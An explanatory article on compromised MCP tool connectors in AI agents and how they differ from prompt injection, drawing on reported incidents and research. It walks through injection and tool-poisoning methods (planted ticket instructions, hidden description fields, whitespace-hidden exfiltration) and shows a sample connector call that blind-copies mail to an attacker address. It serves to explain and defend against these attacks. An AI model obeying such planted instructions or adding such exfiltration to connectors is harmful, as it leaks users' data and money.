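# Compromised Tool Connectors in AI Agent Systems: How They Differ from Prompt Injection, and How to Limit and Stop Them

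## What is a tool connector, and what authority does it hold?

A tool connector is a program that carries out an AI agent's requests on an outside service, such as a mailbox, a payment processor or a database. An agent is a language model that software runs in a loop, so that the model can call tools, read the results and decide what to do next. The model only produces text, so the connector sends the email or moves the money, using credentials that the outside service accepts.

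Those credentials make connectors worth attacking. A connector is compromised if an attacker controls its code, updates, server or credentials, including if it was malicious from the start. The attacker can then use its credentials directly, so even a perfectly behaved model cannot prevent this.

Most new connectors follow the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for how AI applications discover and call tools. The AI company Anthropic released it in November 2024. *When MCP Servers Attack* (Zhao, Liu and colleagues, 2025) points out that developers previously wrote custom connectors or relied on agent frameworks such as LangChain and AutoGen, and that both took a lot of work. With MCP, a developer can write a connector once and use it in many applications. MCP's term for a connector is "server", which misleads newcomers because many of these servers run on the user's own laptop.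 In Anthropic's products, the label for an MCP server is "connector".

Plugins and ordinary API integrations (an API is the interface through which one program calls another) raise the same issue. If a company writes forty lines of code to let its agent call a payment service, that code holds a payment key, and an attacker who controls the code can use the key. MCP matters because it made such programs easy to publish and install.

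### One refund, step by step

In an invented example, an online shop's support agent has three connectors: a ticket reader, a mail sender and a refund connector. A customer writes that a $40 kettle arrived cracked, and a staff member asks the agent to handle the ticket.

Before the model receives the request, the host, which is the application that runs the model, has already requested a list of tools from each connector. Each entry gives the tool's name, a description in ordinary language and a schema, which formally specifies the inputs the tool accepts. The host merges these lists and sends them to the model with the request.

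The model calls the ticket reader, gets the customer's message back, and then produces a short piece of structured text that names another tool and fills in its inputs. In MCP's format the core of it would look like this:

```json
{ "name": "issue_refund",
  "arguments": { "charge_id": "1042", "amount": 40 } }
```

No money has moved yet. The host intercepts this text and can stop it. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the part of the specification that governs calls, recommends but does not require that a person always be able to deny a call. It leaves the form of any approval screen to the application.

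If the call goes ahead, the host passes it to the refund connector with some metadata, such as the protocol version. The message doesn't include the payment key, which the shop stored in the connector's settings during installation. The connector rewrites the request in the format the payment processor expects, attaches the key and sends it. The processor checks the key and the charge number, but it can't check whether the refund is for a cracked kettle because it doesn't receive the ticket or the conversation.

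The processor then refunds the $40 and returns a record to the connector. The connector writes a result, often a line or two of text, which the host adds to the conversation. The model reads the result and drafts an apology for the mail sender to deliver. The connector's result is the model's only source of information about the refund.

### Where the credential sits

The model normally never receives the key. A connector on the user's machine can take its credentials from its environment, a set of values that the host supplies when it starts the connector. The Model Context Protocol project's guide to local servers shows a sample configuration file that contains the key for a search service.

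A connector on someone else's machine usually involves two credentials. The host presents one to the connector to show that the user may use it, and the connector presents the other to the outside service. MCP has rules for the first exchange. Stack Overflow's *Is that allowed? Authentication and authorization in Model Context Protocol* (2026) explains that the second is outside the specification, and that the connector logs in to the service as any other program would.

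Large agent platforms go further to keep secrets away from the model. Anthropic stores them in a vault outside the sandbox (the sealed-off environment where the model's code runs), and a separate proxy fetches them when a call needs them. OpenAI gives code in its sandbox a placeholder, which a network proxy swaps for the real secret when the code sends a request to an approved address.

These designs protect against a model revealing a key or code copying one, but they do less to prevent misuse. Code that holds only a placeholder can still send an approved address any request that the real secret permits. Simpler set-ups can also expose the key when a user pastes it into the chat, or when an agent with permission to open files reads a configuration file that stores the key in plain text.

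### Local and remote connectors

MCP distinguishes between hosts, clients and servers. The host is the application, such as Claude Desktop or the code editor Visual Studio Code. It creates one client within itself for each connector, and that client only maintains the link to its connector. The server is the connector. The Model Context Protocol (2026) overview uses "server" for this program wherever it runs.

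The separation has a security purpose. According to Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), the full conversation should stay with the host, and no connector should be able to read all of it or see into another connector. But the US National Security Agency's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) warns that a client may share information so freely that it is exposed to several servers at once. Even perfect separation limits only what a connector can read from the conversation, not what it does with its own credentials.

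A local connector is a separate program that the host starts on the user's machine, and by default it runs with the user's rights. Model Context Protocol's guide gives the example of a file-management connector whose configuration names two folders, Desktop and Downloads. The connector's own code has to enforce that limit. The operating system applies the permissions of the user's account, and the guide says the program can perform any file operation that the user could perform by hand. Unless someone confines it, even a local connector that only fetches weather forecasts can open the user's documents and saved login files. For this reason, Model Context Protocol's *Security best practices* recommends running local servers in a sandbox with minimal privileges. *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026), a study of unapproved agents on company computers, quotes the specification's caution that tools "represent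 arbitrary code execution".

A remote connector runs on someone else's computers, and the host reaches it over the internet. It has no direct access to the user's disk, which removes the most serious risk of a local connector, but the user has to trust an operator whose running code they cannot inspect. A remote connector also typically serves many clients, so one machine may hold working credentials for many customers. The risk also depends on who the operator is. Sentry, which tracks software errors, runs the official connector to its own service, so a customer who uses it hands data to a company that already had it. If a third party ran that connector, one more organisation would have access to the customer's account.

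A connector's authority is everything the program can do with the credentials and system access it holds, whether or not anyone intended it. The tool list is a poor measure of this authority. A connector may list a single tool called "look up order" but hold a database password that can delete every order in the shop.

### Tokens, scopes and expiry

Most credentials in this field are tokens, which are strings of characters that a service issues and later accepts as proof of permission. The most common kind is the bearer token. A service grants access to anyone who presents one, so a thief with a copy gets the same access as the owner.

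Two properties limit the damage. The first is scope, the set of operations the token permits. A mail token might let its holder read messages but not send them, but scopes can also be very wide. The NSA gives the example of the connector for GitHub, the code-hosting site, where users granted blanket access and the tools could then read and write across both private and public repositories.

The second is expiry. A short-lived token stops working after a set time, such as an hour, and the issuer can revoke it sooner. Many services also issue a refresh token, used only to obtain new access tokens, so that users don't have to keep logging in. The vaults described in Anthropic's *Authenticate with vaults* can renew tokens this way without involving the user. Expiry therefore does little to stop an attacker who also holds the refresh token. Many API keys have no expiry date and work until someone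 cancels them.

The NSA noted in its May 2026 guidance that authorization in MCP is optional and that the core specification does not require tokens to expire. A July 2026 revision tightened the authorization rules, but a connector's authority still depends mostly on which credential someone gives it.

### Injection, least privilege and the confused deputy

In a prompt injection, an attacker plants text where a model will read it, and the model follows the instructions in that text. This works because models take in instructions and data through the same channel and cannot reliably tell them apart. At the shop, a customer could end a complaint with a line telling the agent to refund the last twenty orders as well. In the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), six security agencies from five countries describe a similar case, in which instructions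 in a phishing email lead a mail-monitoring agent to download malware.

Least privilege is the rule that each component gets only the authority its task needs. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) lists it as a design principle because it limits the damage from an accident or error. It also leaves fewer privileged programs interacting, and so fewer chances for one to misuse another. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners describe a typical breach, in which a calendar assistant can see everyone's meetings but needs only those of the person asking.

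A confused deputy is a program that is tricked into using its legitimate authority on behalf of someone who lacks that authority. The term comes from *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988), which tells a nearly true story about Tymshare, a computer-sharing company. Tymshare gave its compiler, a program that translates code, permission to write in a system folder so that it could record usage statistics. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. One user named the company's billing file, which was in the same folder. The user wasn't allowed to change that file, but the compiler was, and it overwrote the billing records. Hardy traced the fault to the compiler running with authority "stemming from two sources", its own and the user's, with no way to keep the two apart.

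The shop's refund connector is in the same position as the compiler when a planted instruction leads the model to request a refund that nobody is owed. The connector's code is sound and its key is valid, but it spends the shop's money on a stranger's behalf. A related problem arises in the Model Context Protocol (MCP) when a connector logs in to an outside service under one fixed identity for all its users. MCP's security guidance describes how an attacker can exploit a user's earlier consent to gain access that the user never approved.

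### How widely people use connectors

The available figures for connector use are large but indirect. In July 2026, the Model Context Protocol (2026) project reported nearly half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits, the libraries developers use to build hosts and connectors. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) put the figure at more than 400 million, four times the level at the start of the year. It also reported that the company's own directory had over 950 connectors, which millions of people use every day. Downloads overstate the number of users because automated systems fetch the same package repeatedly. Anthropic's count of daily users is probably a better guide to everyday use, though it covers only one company's products.

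What the connectors do has also changed. In *How are AI agents used?*, a study from the UK AI Security Institute, Stein (2026) catalogued 177,436 tools that developers published between November 2024 and February 2026. Stein distinguished tools that read or analyse from "action" tools, which change something outside the conversation, such as by editing a file, sending a message or making a payment. Measured again by downloads, action tools rose from 27% to 65% of use over those sixteen months. Stein could obtain download counts for 3,854 connectors, and software development accounted for 90% of the downloads. Most action tools supported medium-stakes work such as editing files, but tools for financial transactions were growing fast.

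### What the support agent can do

The shop's refund connector belongs to that last group. To use invented figures, the agent makes about 100 refunds a day averaging $40, or about $4,000 a day. The connector's payment key can refund any past charge on the shop's account, and those charges total $600,000. At its normal pace the agent would take 150 days to refund that much, but the key has no rate limit, so whoever holds it can send requests as fast as the payment processor will accept them. The mail sender can write to any address in the shop's name. The ticket reader cannot change anything, but it brings text from strangers into the conversation all day.

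## How does a compromised connector differ from an injected prompt?

A prompt injection works only if the model obeys the planted text. A compromised connector acts after the model has made its request, so even a correct request can end in theft. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (Errico, Ngiam and Sojan, 2025) also distinguishes attackers who hide instructions in otherwise legitimate data from attackers who distribute compromised servers. Either kind of attacker could target the shop's mail sender.

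### Instructions hidden in a ticket

An attacker opens a ticket about a late parcel. Below the complaint, the attacker adds instructions, disguised as an internal notice, for the agent to email the ten most recent tickets to an outside address before replying. The attacker needs only the shop's public contact form, not a password or any software.

A staff member asks the agent to handle the ticket. The model calls the ticket reader, which adds the whole message to the conversation, including the planted paragraph. If the model treats the paragraph as part of a customer's message, it writes an apology for the late parcel and the attack fails. If it treats the paragraph as an instruction, it fetches the ten tickets and produces a call to the mail sender, with the attacker's address in the recipient field and ten customers' names and complaints in the body.

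The host receives that call before anything leaves the shop. If the shop requires approval for outgoing mail, a staff member can see the strange address and refuse. Otherwise, in another instance of the confused deputy problem, the mail sender attaches its key and sends exactly what the model requested.

### A mail sender that adds a recipient

Now suppose that the attacker controls the mail sender's code. A real customer writes about a cracked kettle, and the ticket contains no instructions of any kind. The model drafts an apology and makes this call:

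```json
{ "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": { "to": "customer@example.com",
                 "subject": "Your kettle",
                 "body": "We are sorry it arrived cracked." } }
```

The request is correct, and a staff member who checks it will rightly approve it. The connector then passes a slightly different message to the mail service:

```json
{ "to": "customer@example.com",
  "bcc": "attacker@example.net",
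  "subject": "Your kettle",
  "body": "We are sorry it arrived cracked." }
```

The extra line adds a blind copy, which the customer can't see. The mail service accepts the message because the key is valid. The connector returns "Email sent", the model reports success, and the customer gets the apology. A real mail connector called postmark-mcp did the same thing to its users in September 2025.

A compromised connector can also act without a call from the agent. It holds the key to the shop's email account whenever it is running, so it can email every customer whose address it has handled and ask for card details in the shop's name. The model isn't involved, so the host has no tool call to record.

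### Approval, logs and duration

| | Instructions in a ticket | Compromised mail sender |
|---|---|---|
| What the attacker controls | Some of the text that the model reads | The program that holds the mail key |
| Does a model that resists planted instructions stop it? | Yes | No |
| Does an approval prompt show the harmful act? | Yes, to someone who reads all of it | No, it shows the model's correct request |
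| Are the host's logs truthful? | Yes | Truthful about the request, but not about what the connector did with it |
| How long does it last? | Usually one conversation | Until someone stops the connector and cancels its key |

Approval prompts are weaker in practice than the table suggests. Anthropic found that its users approved about 93% of them, according to *Anthropic Just Made the Case for MCP Gateways* (nate, 2026), a blog post from Zuplo, which sells gateway software. Reading the prompts more carefully would still help against the ticket attack, since the attacker's address is in the request, but not against the blind copy, because everything on the screen is correct.

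The logs have a similar gap. The host records the model's request and the connector's reply, but in the second attack the attacker writes that reply. To find the blind copy, the shop would have to check the mail service's records, which list every recipient.

Even a service's records can be misleading if the attacker has stolen a credential. eSecurity Planet's *Claude Code MCP Attack Enables Persistent Token Theft* describes an attack on Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent. A malicious software package changes the connector addresses in the agent's settings file so that traffic passes through the attacker's machine, which collects the login tokens. When the attacker misuses those tokens, the activity may look normal in the service's audit log because the requests come from trusted infrastructure.

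The same attack is hard to end. If the victim replaces the stolen token but leaves the package in place, the package can redirect the traffic again and send the attacker the new token. An ordinary malicious connector also survives a restart, because most hosts start every registered connector at each launch without asking the user again, as Zhao and colleagues found.

An injected ticket normally loses its effect when the conversation ends. But it can work again if the agent rereads the ticket in a later conversation or has saved the planted text to long-term memory. The shop should therefore close the conversation and delete the planted text.

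### Twelve attacks by a malicious connector

Zhao and colleagues give the fullest account of what a malicious connector can do. Their September 2025 paper assumes that the attacker writes and publishes the connector, and that the model, host and user are all honest. It sorts attacks into twelve categories by the part of the connector that carries them.

Besides tools, an MCP connector can offer resources and prompts. A resource is data to read, such as a log file. A prompt, in MCP's sense, is a ready-made request, such as "review this code", that the user picks from a menu. Tools, resources and prompts each have metadata (a name and description), logic (code) and output.

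The table below regroups the twelve categories by attack route. The percentages are average success rates from the team's tests. The examples illustrate each category and aren't always the versions the team tested.

| Route | Category | Example | Average success |
|---|---|---|---|
| The model | Connector metadata | A fake connector calls itself "official-paypal-server" | 94% |
| The model | Tool metadata | A description says the tool must run after every other tool and receive its output | 89.3% |
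| The model | Tool output | A memo tool's result says to email the memo to an outsider | 100% |
| The model | Resource metadata | A resource falsely claims to carry expensive financial data | 66.7% |
| The model | Resource output | A note added to a log says the security problems are already fixed | 67.8% |
| The model | Prompt output | A code-review request gains a line saying to always approve the code | 46.7% |
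| User or host settings | Configuration | Launch settings that the user copies give the connector the whole disk | 100% |
| User or host settings | Prompt metadata | A form asks the user for needless personal details | No rate |
| Code alone | Start-up code | The connector installs a back door when it launches | 100% |
| Code alone | Tool logic | A tool sends its inputs to the attacker as well as doing its job | 100% |
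| Code alone | Resource logic | Opening a resource runs hidden code | 100% |
| Code alone | Prompt logic | Picking a ready-made request runs hidden code | 100% |

Some categories fit more than one route. A false name can fool a person browsing a directory as easily as a model, and in some hosts the user chooses resources, so a misleading description has to fool the user. A tool's code can also open a form that asks the user for a government ID number. But all four categories of code attack include versions that work without anyone making a further mistake once the connector is installed and in use.

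These four kinds of code run at different times. Start-up code runs as soon as the host launches the connector, before the user has typed anything. On a local connector, it can act with the user's rights. Tool code runs when the model calls the tool, as with the mail sender. Resource code runs when someone opens the resource. Prompt code runs when the user picks a ready-made request, without involving the model.

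Neither the host nor the model can normally see this code, and two security scanners the team tried missed many of the malicious connectors. Reading a remote connector's published source may not help either. The software security company OX Security warns in The Hacker News' *Welcome to the Jungle* (2026) that the code on the operator's server can differ entirely from that in the public repository.

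### Results across hosts and models

To measure these success rates, Zhao and colleagues built one malicious connector for each category and installed it locally. The hosts were Claude Desktop, the code editor Cursor, and an application they built with the open-source framework fast-agent. The models were OpenAI's GPT-4o and o3, Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 4 and Claude Opus 4, and Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro. These were among the leading models of mid-2025, but much stronger ones have since replaced them.

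The team ran most attacks 15 times on each of ten host-model pairings, each time in a new conversation. A run counted as a success if the attack achieved its aim and neither the host nor the model blocked it. Cursor has no results for the attacks that use resource code, prompt code or their output, so those averages cover six pairings. The team tested misleading resource descriptions separately on the five models, because none of the three hosts let the model choose resources. The team reported no success rate for misleading prompt descriptions, which target people.

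All four code attacks succeeded in every run, which shows that the hosts didn't check whether a connector's behaviour matched its stated purpose. The models never had a chance to refuse, so the result isn't evidence that they were weak. A host that confined its connectors should have done better with the same models.

The results of attacks that worked through the model varied much more. With GPT-4o, the poisoned tool description succeeded every time in fast-agent and never in Cursor. The team suspected that the system prompt, the text a host gives the model before the conversation starts, caused the difference. When they put Cursor's system prompt into fast-agent, the success rate fell from 100% to 6.7%, or one run in fifteen.

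The way a host presents text to the model also affected the results. Claude Sonnet 4 followed malicious instructions in a resource in every run on Claude Desktop, which passes resources to the model as text files, but in only 13.3% of runs on fast-agent, which inserts them into the user's input. Responses to misleading resource descriptions varied widely by model. GPT-4o and Gemini 2.5 Pro picked the malicious resource every time, while o3 picked it in 13.3% of runs and usually chose no resource, citing doubts about authenticity.

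So model makers and host developers can both reduce these attacks. The exception is malicious tool output, which works through the model but succeeded in every run because no host filtered the output and every model passed the harmful content on to the user.

Better training should help a model ignore instructions in tool output, but it helps less with false statements. If the refund connector reports that it has refunded $40 and it hasn't, the model has no other source to check. Zhao and colleagues give the example of an investment tool that offers accurate analysis for a while and then recommends a stock the attacker chose. A model could repeat that advice without breaking any of its rules.

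### Tool poisoning

Many real attacks combine the two threats. One way to tell the threats apart is to imagine a careful employee, who never follows planted instructions, in the model's place. If the harm would still happen, the organization has to restrict the connector itself.

Tool poisoning is prompt injection placed in a connector's description of its own tools. *MCP Security Notification* (Invariant Labs, 2025) introduced the term. The attacker controls the connector, but the attack works only if the model follows the instructions in the description, which a careful employee would ignore.

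The software developer Simon Willison gives the example of a tool that adds two numbers. The tool also has a text field called "sidenote", and its description instructs the model to read a private file and put the contents in that field. The tool's code sends the sidenote to the attacker and then returns the correct sum.

An attacker whose code already runs on the user's computer hardly needs this trick, because the code could usually open the file itself. The trick is more useful when the connector is remote or sandboxed, because it lets the attacker use the access of the agent and its other connectors, which may be far broader than the malicious connector's own.

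Invariant Labs' *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrates this borrowing. The agent had a trusted connector for WhatsApp and a second connector that the attacker controlled. The second connector offered only a "fact of the day" tool. The tool's description was harmless when it first launched, and the user approved it.

On the second launch, the connector supplied a different description with instructions for sending WhatsApp messages. The model was to replace the recipient with a number described as a proxy and add earlier chats to the message. The host didn't alert the user to the change. When the agent next sent an ordinary message, the user's chat history went to the attacker.

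The agent never had to call the fact tool. The trusted WhatsApp connector carried out the leak in response to a technically valid request. Invariant Labs points out that sandboxing the malicious connector would not stop the attack, which only requires the model to follow the malicious instructions.

Cursor asked the user to approve the message, but the dialog showed a bare phone number and what appeared to be just "Hi". A long run of spaces pushed the stolen text out of view to the right, and Cursor hid the scrollbar. A better dialog would have exposed this attack, though no dialog could have exposed the blind copy in the mail example.

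Two days after publishing, Invariant Labs added an experiment with no malicious connector. The attacker sent the victim a WhatsApp message containing similar instructions. The agent read the message while listing recent chats, then leaked the victim's contacts. This version took more work because the text had to imitate the end of a message record before the model would follow it. Invariant Labs suspected that models give less weight to tool results than to tool descriptions. The two experiments show that such attacks are possible, but Invariant Labs reported no success rate for either.

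A poisoned description also lasts longer than a planted message, because the host can supply it to the model in every new conversation. The attacker can leave it dormant until a trigger appears. Trail of Bits' *How MCP servers can steal your conversation history* (2025) describes a tool whose instructions take effect only when the user types a common phrase such as "thank you", at which point the model forwards the whole conversation so far. An attacker who chose a trigger that appears only with valuable data, such as an API key, would have less worthless text to sort through.

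Schneider explains in *Why MCP security is different* that the operator of a remote connector can rewrite its description at any moment, while changing a local connector's description normally requires a package update. An update gives users a chance to compare the old and new text, though Schneider thinks few do.

If the model ignores the poisoned text, that attack fails. The shop should still remove the connector and cancel its credentials, because whoever wrote the description probably also controls the connector's code and can use it for an attack that doesn't depend on the model.

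### Honest connectors that cause harm

An attacker can sometimes use a connector's authority without controlling the connector, by exploiting a flaw in it. *CVE-2026-46555*, an entry in OSV, a public database of software flaws, describes such a flaw in a WhatsApp connector. Before version 0.2.1, part of the connector accepted commands from other programs on the same computer without asking for a password. Any program running under the same user account could send messages as the user. It could also read any file the user could read, including login keys and browser data, by naming it as an attachment.

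The careful employee couldn't have prevented this, because the attacker's program bypasses the model. In that respect the flaw resembles a compromised connector. But the developer is still honest and can fix the flaw with an update, and until then the attacker can do only what the flaw allows.

Large organisations have made such mistakes too. In *Google, JPMorgan and two governments fixed the same MCP flaw*, Stanciuc (2026) reports the researcher Syed Anas Mohiuddin's account of a server-side request forgery flaw that affected both companies, the French government's digital agency and an Indonesian city. This type of flaw lets an outsider make a server send requests on their behalf. It is dangerous because the server can often reach internal systems that the outsider cannot.

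A more serious flaw can turn a legitimate connector into a compromised one. OX Security's *Anthropic design choice Exposes 150M+ Downloads and up to 200K Servers* describes applications that let user input reach the settings for launching a local connector. Because those settings specify a command to run, an attacker who can change them can run commands on the machine. OX blames the design of Anthropic's MCP software development kits. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *MCP Is Creating Major Governance Gaps, Researchers Warn*, Anthropic called the behaviour expected, leaving individual projects to make their own fixes.

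A deceived model can also cause harm through a connector that works as its developer intended. The ticket attack on the mail sender is the simplest example, but the harmful act isn't always so visible. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* examines a connector that Anthropic published, but no longer maintains, for the workplace chat service Slack. A company might think an agent is safe if it can post only in a private channel, since outsiders can't read its posts there.

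Link previews break that assumption. An attacker plants instructions in a document, and the model follows them by posting a link whose address contains private data. Slack then fetches the page to build a preview, which sends the data to the attacker's server. An approval prompt would show a message going to a permitted channel, so a reviewer would have to inspect the link and know how previews work to spot the leak.

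The careful employee would never have posted the link, so this is still prompt injection. The company could also prevent the leak without changing the model by turning previews off, so the connector's design is worth fixing even when its developer is honest and its code works as intended.

### What a better model can fix

In a test that Infosecurity Magazine reported in September 2026, OX Security attached a malicious connector to Claude Code running Haiku 3.5, a small Anthropic model from 2024. The connector first requested access to a harmless file, and the user approved with the "always allow" option. It then requested sensitive files, including `.env`, where developers commonly store passwords and keys. The connector got that file without the user seeing another prompt.

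Two safeguards failed in this test, because the user had earlier turned off the approval prompt by choosing "always allow" and the model didn't flag a suspicious request. According to OX's summary, Anthropic replied that "always allow" works as documented, and that a model's ability to spot malicious content is a best-effort check that nobody should treat as a security boundary.

A newer model might well have refused the second request. Willison (2026) describes a challenge in which people tried to extract a secret from an agent by sending it emails. The agent ran on Anthropic's Opus 4.6 and had rules against revealing credentials or running commands from emails. Nobody had obtained the secret after 6,000 attempts.

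Persistent attackers do better in other tests. nate cites Anthropic's figures for Opus 4.7, a later model, on a benchmark of attacks against agents. A single injection attempt succeeded about 0.1% of the time, but attackers who could adapt over a hundred attempts succeeded 5% to 6% of the time. An attacker can easily make a hundred attempts on a support desk that accepts tickets from anyone.

Resistance to planted text also does little when the harmful instruction comes from the user. In an exercise that nate recounts, Anthropic's testers tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt to copy cloud credentials to an outside address, and Claude Code did so in 24 of 25 runs. Anthropic concluded that only limits in the agent's environment would work, such as blocking data sent to unapproved addresses.

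OX's malicious connector sent the agent a request for the file, which the model could refuse. A local connector that runs with the user's rights can open `.env` itself. The model receives no request and the user sees no prompt, so replacing Haiku 3.5 with the best model available would not help. A sandbox that blocks the connector's access to the file would stop it.

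## How do connectors become compromised?

In the shop example, the mail sender copied customers' emails to an attacker because the attacker controlled its code. An attacker can gain that control by publishing a fake connector, taking over a real developer's account, or hiding malicious code in a package that the connector needs. Some attackers instead exploit a flaw in the connector's existing code, change the settings file that lists an agent's connectors, or steal the connector's credentials. Researchers have also found connectors listed at expired web addresses that anyone can buy.

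Most local connectors come from GitHub, npm (for JavaScript packages) or PyPI (for Python packages), where anyone can publish. Directories called registries or marketplaces help users find connectors on these sites.

### The postmark-mcp case

Postmark is a service that companies use to send automated emails such as receipts and password resets. It had published the code for an official MCP connector on GitHub but hadn't put a package on npm. In September 2025, a developer with no connection to Postmark copied that code and published it on npm as "postmark-mcp". The Hacker News dates the upload to 15 September and reports that the same account maintained 31 other packages.

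The security company Koi, which discovered the attack, found that the first 15 versions worked properly. The only change in version 1.0.16, released on 17 September, was a new line of code that blind-copied the developer on every email the connector sent. The developer therefore received everything in those emails, including any passwords or invoices.

The case combined impersonation with a malicious update. Someone who reviewed the code before 17 September would have found nothing harmful. They could have noticed that the publisher wasn't Postmark, but checking the developer's reputation would probably have reassured them, because the developer used a real name and had a history of legitimate projects.

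Koi's monitoring software flagged version 1.0.16 because the package's behaviour had changed. Koi asked the developer for an explanation, but the developer did not reply and then deleted the package from npm. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), the public record of the malware, is dated 26 September, nine days after the malicious release. ReversingLabs' *postmark-mcp* also identifies malware in version 1.0.18, so the developer released at least one more version after the first malicious one.

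Deleting the package from npm didn't remove it from users' computers, where it kept sending blind copies of emails. Postmark confirmed that the package was an impersonation and that the attack hadn't affected its own service. It told users to delete the package, check their email logs and consider replacing any credentials they had sent by email.

The Hacker News reports 1,643 total downloads of the package, while Koi reports about 1,500 a week. Both figures could be right, because the package existed for less than two weeks and could have had most of its downloads in one week. The malicious version came only two days after the first upload, although Koi describes a tool that could be "legitimate for months" before it turned malicious. The package had fifteen releases in those two days, which may have been an attempt to make it look established.

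Nobody has published a count of the victims or the stolen emails. Koi made what it called a rough guess of 3,000 to 15,000 stolen emails a day, based on its weekly download figure. It assumed that about 20% of downloads were in active use, which gave 300 organisations, and that each sent 10 to 50 emails a day. This treats every active download as a separate organisation, although one company can download a package many times. Koi's claim that the attacker stole thousands of emails is still plausible, because ten organisations that each sent 50 emails a day would have lost 4,500 in nine days.

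### Fake connectors

Other impersonators publish a malicious package from the start. OSV's *MAL-2026-5481* (2026) recorded one such case in June 2026. The official MCP connector for the PostgreSQL database has a package name that begins with its publisher's prefix, and someone registered the same name on npm without the prefix. The fake package ran a script during installation that sent details such as the computer's name to an outside address, even if the user never started the connector.

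The security company Apiiro reported a more elaborate case in late November 2026. The Hacker News' *Fake MCP Servers on GitHub Target Claude and Cursor Users with Crypto-Stealing* (2026) describes two connectors presented as tools for customers of the cryptocurrency exchanges Lighter and Aster to check their trading volume and eligibility for token giveaways. Users had to copy the code from GitHub and add it to an agent such as Claude or Cursor.

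When Apiiro started one of the connectors on an isolated Windows machine, the connector began installing the packages it needed and fetched its malware about 18 seconds later. The agent had not yet called any tool, so no approval prompt had appeared. One part of the malware watched the clipboard. If the user copied a cryptocurrency address, it substituted one of 23 addresses belonging to the attackers, and the user's next payment went to them.

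The attackers' wallets received about $49,900 at mid-November prices. Not all of that is confirmed as losses, and Apiiro did not publish the number of victims.

The attackers attracted users by making their projects look popular and active on GitHub. Of the 1,319 accounts that had starred, copied or posted on the projects that Apiiro measured, 1,222 appeared to be fake accounts created in batches. A bot made almost all of the 26,511 recorded code changes. One of the attackers' projects came first in 18 of 54 searches that a developer might run.

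FakeGit, another campaign, used about 7,600 fraudulent GitHub projects to spread malware. According to Help Net Security's *Stolen AI API keys are paying for hackers' autonomous scans* (2026), more than 800 of them posed as MCP connectors or as skills, which are packaged instructions for agents. One imitated Docker's MCP Gateway, which companies use to control their connectors. The security company Bitsight found that mentions of AI agents, MCP and indirect prompt injection on 16 criminal forums rose by 67% from February to August 2026. These mentions are weak evidence of actual attacks, but the increase suggests that interest is growing.

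Marketplaces don't reliably keep fakes out. In a test described in *The MCP Supply Chain Risk*, OX Security submitted a malicious connector to 11 marketplaces. Nine accepted it without review, and only GitHub's managed registry blocked it. Fakes also get into marketplaces for related software. *Malicious Claude Code Extension Served in Cursor Supply Chain Attack* (Arghire, 2026) reports that an attacker published a fake Claude Code extension in Cursor's marketplace. The extension collected information about the computer and tried to open a connection that would let the attacker back in.

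### What installation guides recommend

Many users install connectors by copying a command from a guide. *Breaking the Protocol* (Maloyan and Namiot, 2026) surveyed 127 guides to installing MCP connectors and found that 73% had users run the connector directly from a GitHub address with `npx`, without checking the code's integrity. The `npx` command downloads a package and runs it in one step, without a pause for the user to review the code. If the address leads to an impostor's project, the impostor's code runs immediately.

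Maloyan and Namiot also list four ways in which malicious connectors reach users, with a percentage for each:

| Route | Share |
|---|---|
| Package names that resemble a real one | 34% |
| Compromise of a popular connector or a package it depends on | 28% |
| Tutorials and documentation that send users to malicious projects | 23% |
| Marketplaces that do little vetting | 15% |

The four percentages come from a survey of installation guides, which contain advice to users and not records of what attackers did, so they can't show what share of real attacks each represents. The paper doesn't explain how Maloyan and Namiot chose the guides or arrived at the percentages. The 73% figure is more useful because anyone can read a guide and see whether it includes a check. But it describes only these 127 guides, and a guide that omits a check may still lead to a safe connector.

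### Hijacked updates and dependencies

A user who installs a genuine connector can still receive malicious code later. In September 2026, an attacker used the maintainer's account to publish a malicious version of dforge-mcp, a genuine connector on npm. Infosecurity Magazine's *Attackers Abuse npm Trusted Publishing in GHAPPIER Campaign* reports the findings of CloudSEK, a security company that reconstructed the attack.

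Like many projects, dforge-mcp used an automated script on GitHub to build each new version and upload it to npm. npm accepted uploads from that script without a separate password, so anyone who could change the project's main code could publish a new version. The attacker already had access to change that code. CloudSEK couldn't determine how the attacker got this access, but suspects that malware had infected a developer's computer.

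The attacker first changed three lines so that any change to the main code would start the script. Fourteen minutes later, the attacker rewrote the script so that it could publish without human involvement. The first malicious version didn't install properly, but the second worked and remained the latest version for about 35 minutes. Its code ran when a host launched the connector and eventually gave the attacker remote control of the computer.

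The malicious version carried a valid signature because it came from the project's real publishing system. CloudSEK found no sign that the attacker had exploited a flaw in GitHub or npm, and described every step as an "authorised action taken with a stolen key". It also found no evidence that the attack had compromised any organisation.

A connector also runs code from its dependencies, the packages by other developers that it relies on. An attacker who compromises one popular dependency can reach many connectors at once. In March 2026, a criminal group called TeamPCP compromised LiteLLM, an open-source tool that connects applications to AI models. The malicious versions were on PyPI for about 40 minutes. LiteLLM isn't an MCP connector, but any connector that loaded one of those versions would have run the attackers' code with access to its credentials.

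Even 40 minutes was long enough for many software pipelines, the automated systems that build and test software, to download the package. Pipelines often download packages without anyone looking at them. CloudSEK (2026) linked about 434,000 pipelines at more than 2,500 organisations to the incident. These figures are estimates of who may have been exposed, and CloudSEK warns that an organisation's presence in its data doesn't mean it was breached.

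Pinning a connector to a known version doesn't always pin its dependencies. *Your pinned MCP server may not be as pinned as you think* (Zorz, 2026) reports tests by the security company Corelight in which pinned connectors silently downloaded new dependencies.

An update can also compromise a connector that the user has already approved. Docker, whose software runs programs in isolation from the rest of a computer, had to fix such a problem in its Sandboxes product. According to The Hacker News' *Docker Sandboxes Flaw Lets Malicious AI Agent Kit Updates Steal Developers' API* (2026), once a user had approved a third-party agent kit, a malicious update to it could redirect the user's API keys to an attacker's server without the user approving the update.

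### The dispute over MCP's launch mechanism

A host launches a local connector and exchanges messages with it through the connector's standard input and output, which MCP calls the stdio transport. In April 2026, OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* criticised Anthropic's software kits for running whatever launch command the settings contain, without checking that it starts a connector.

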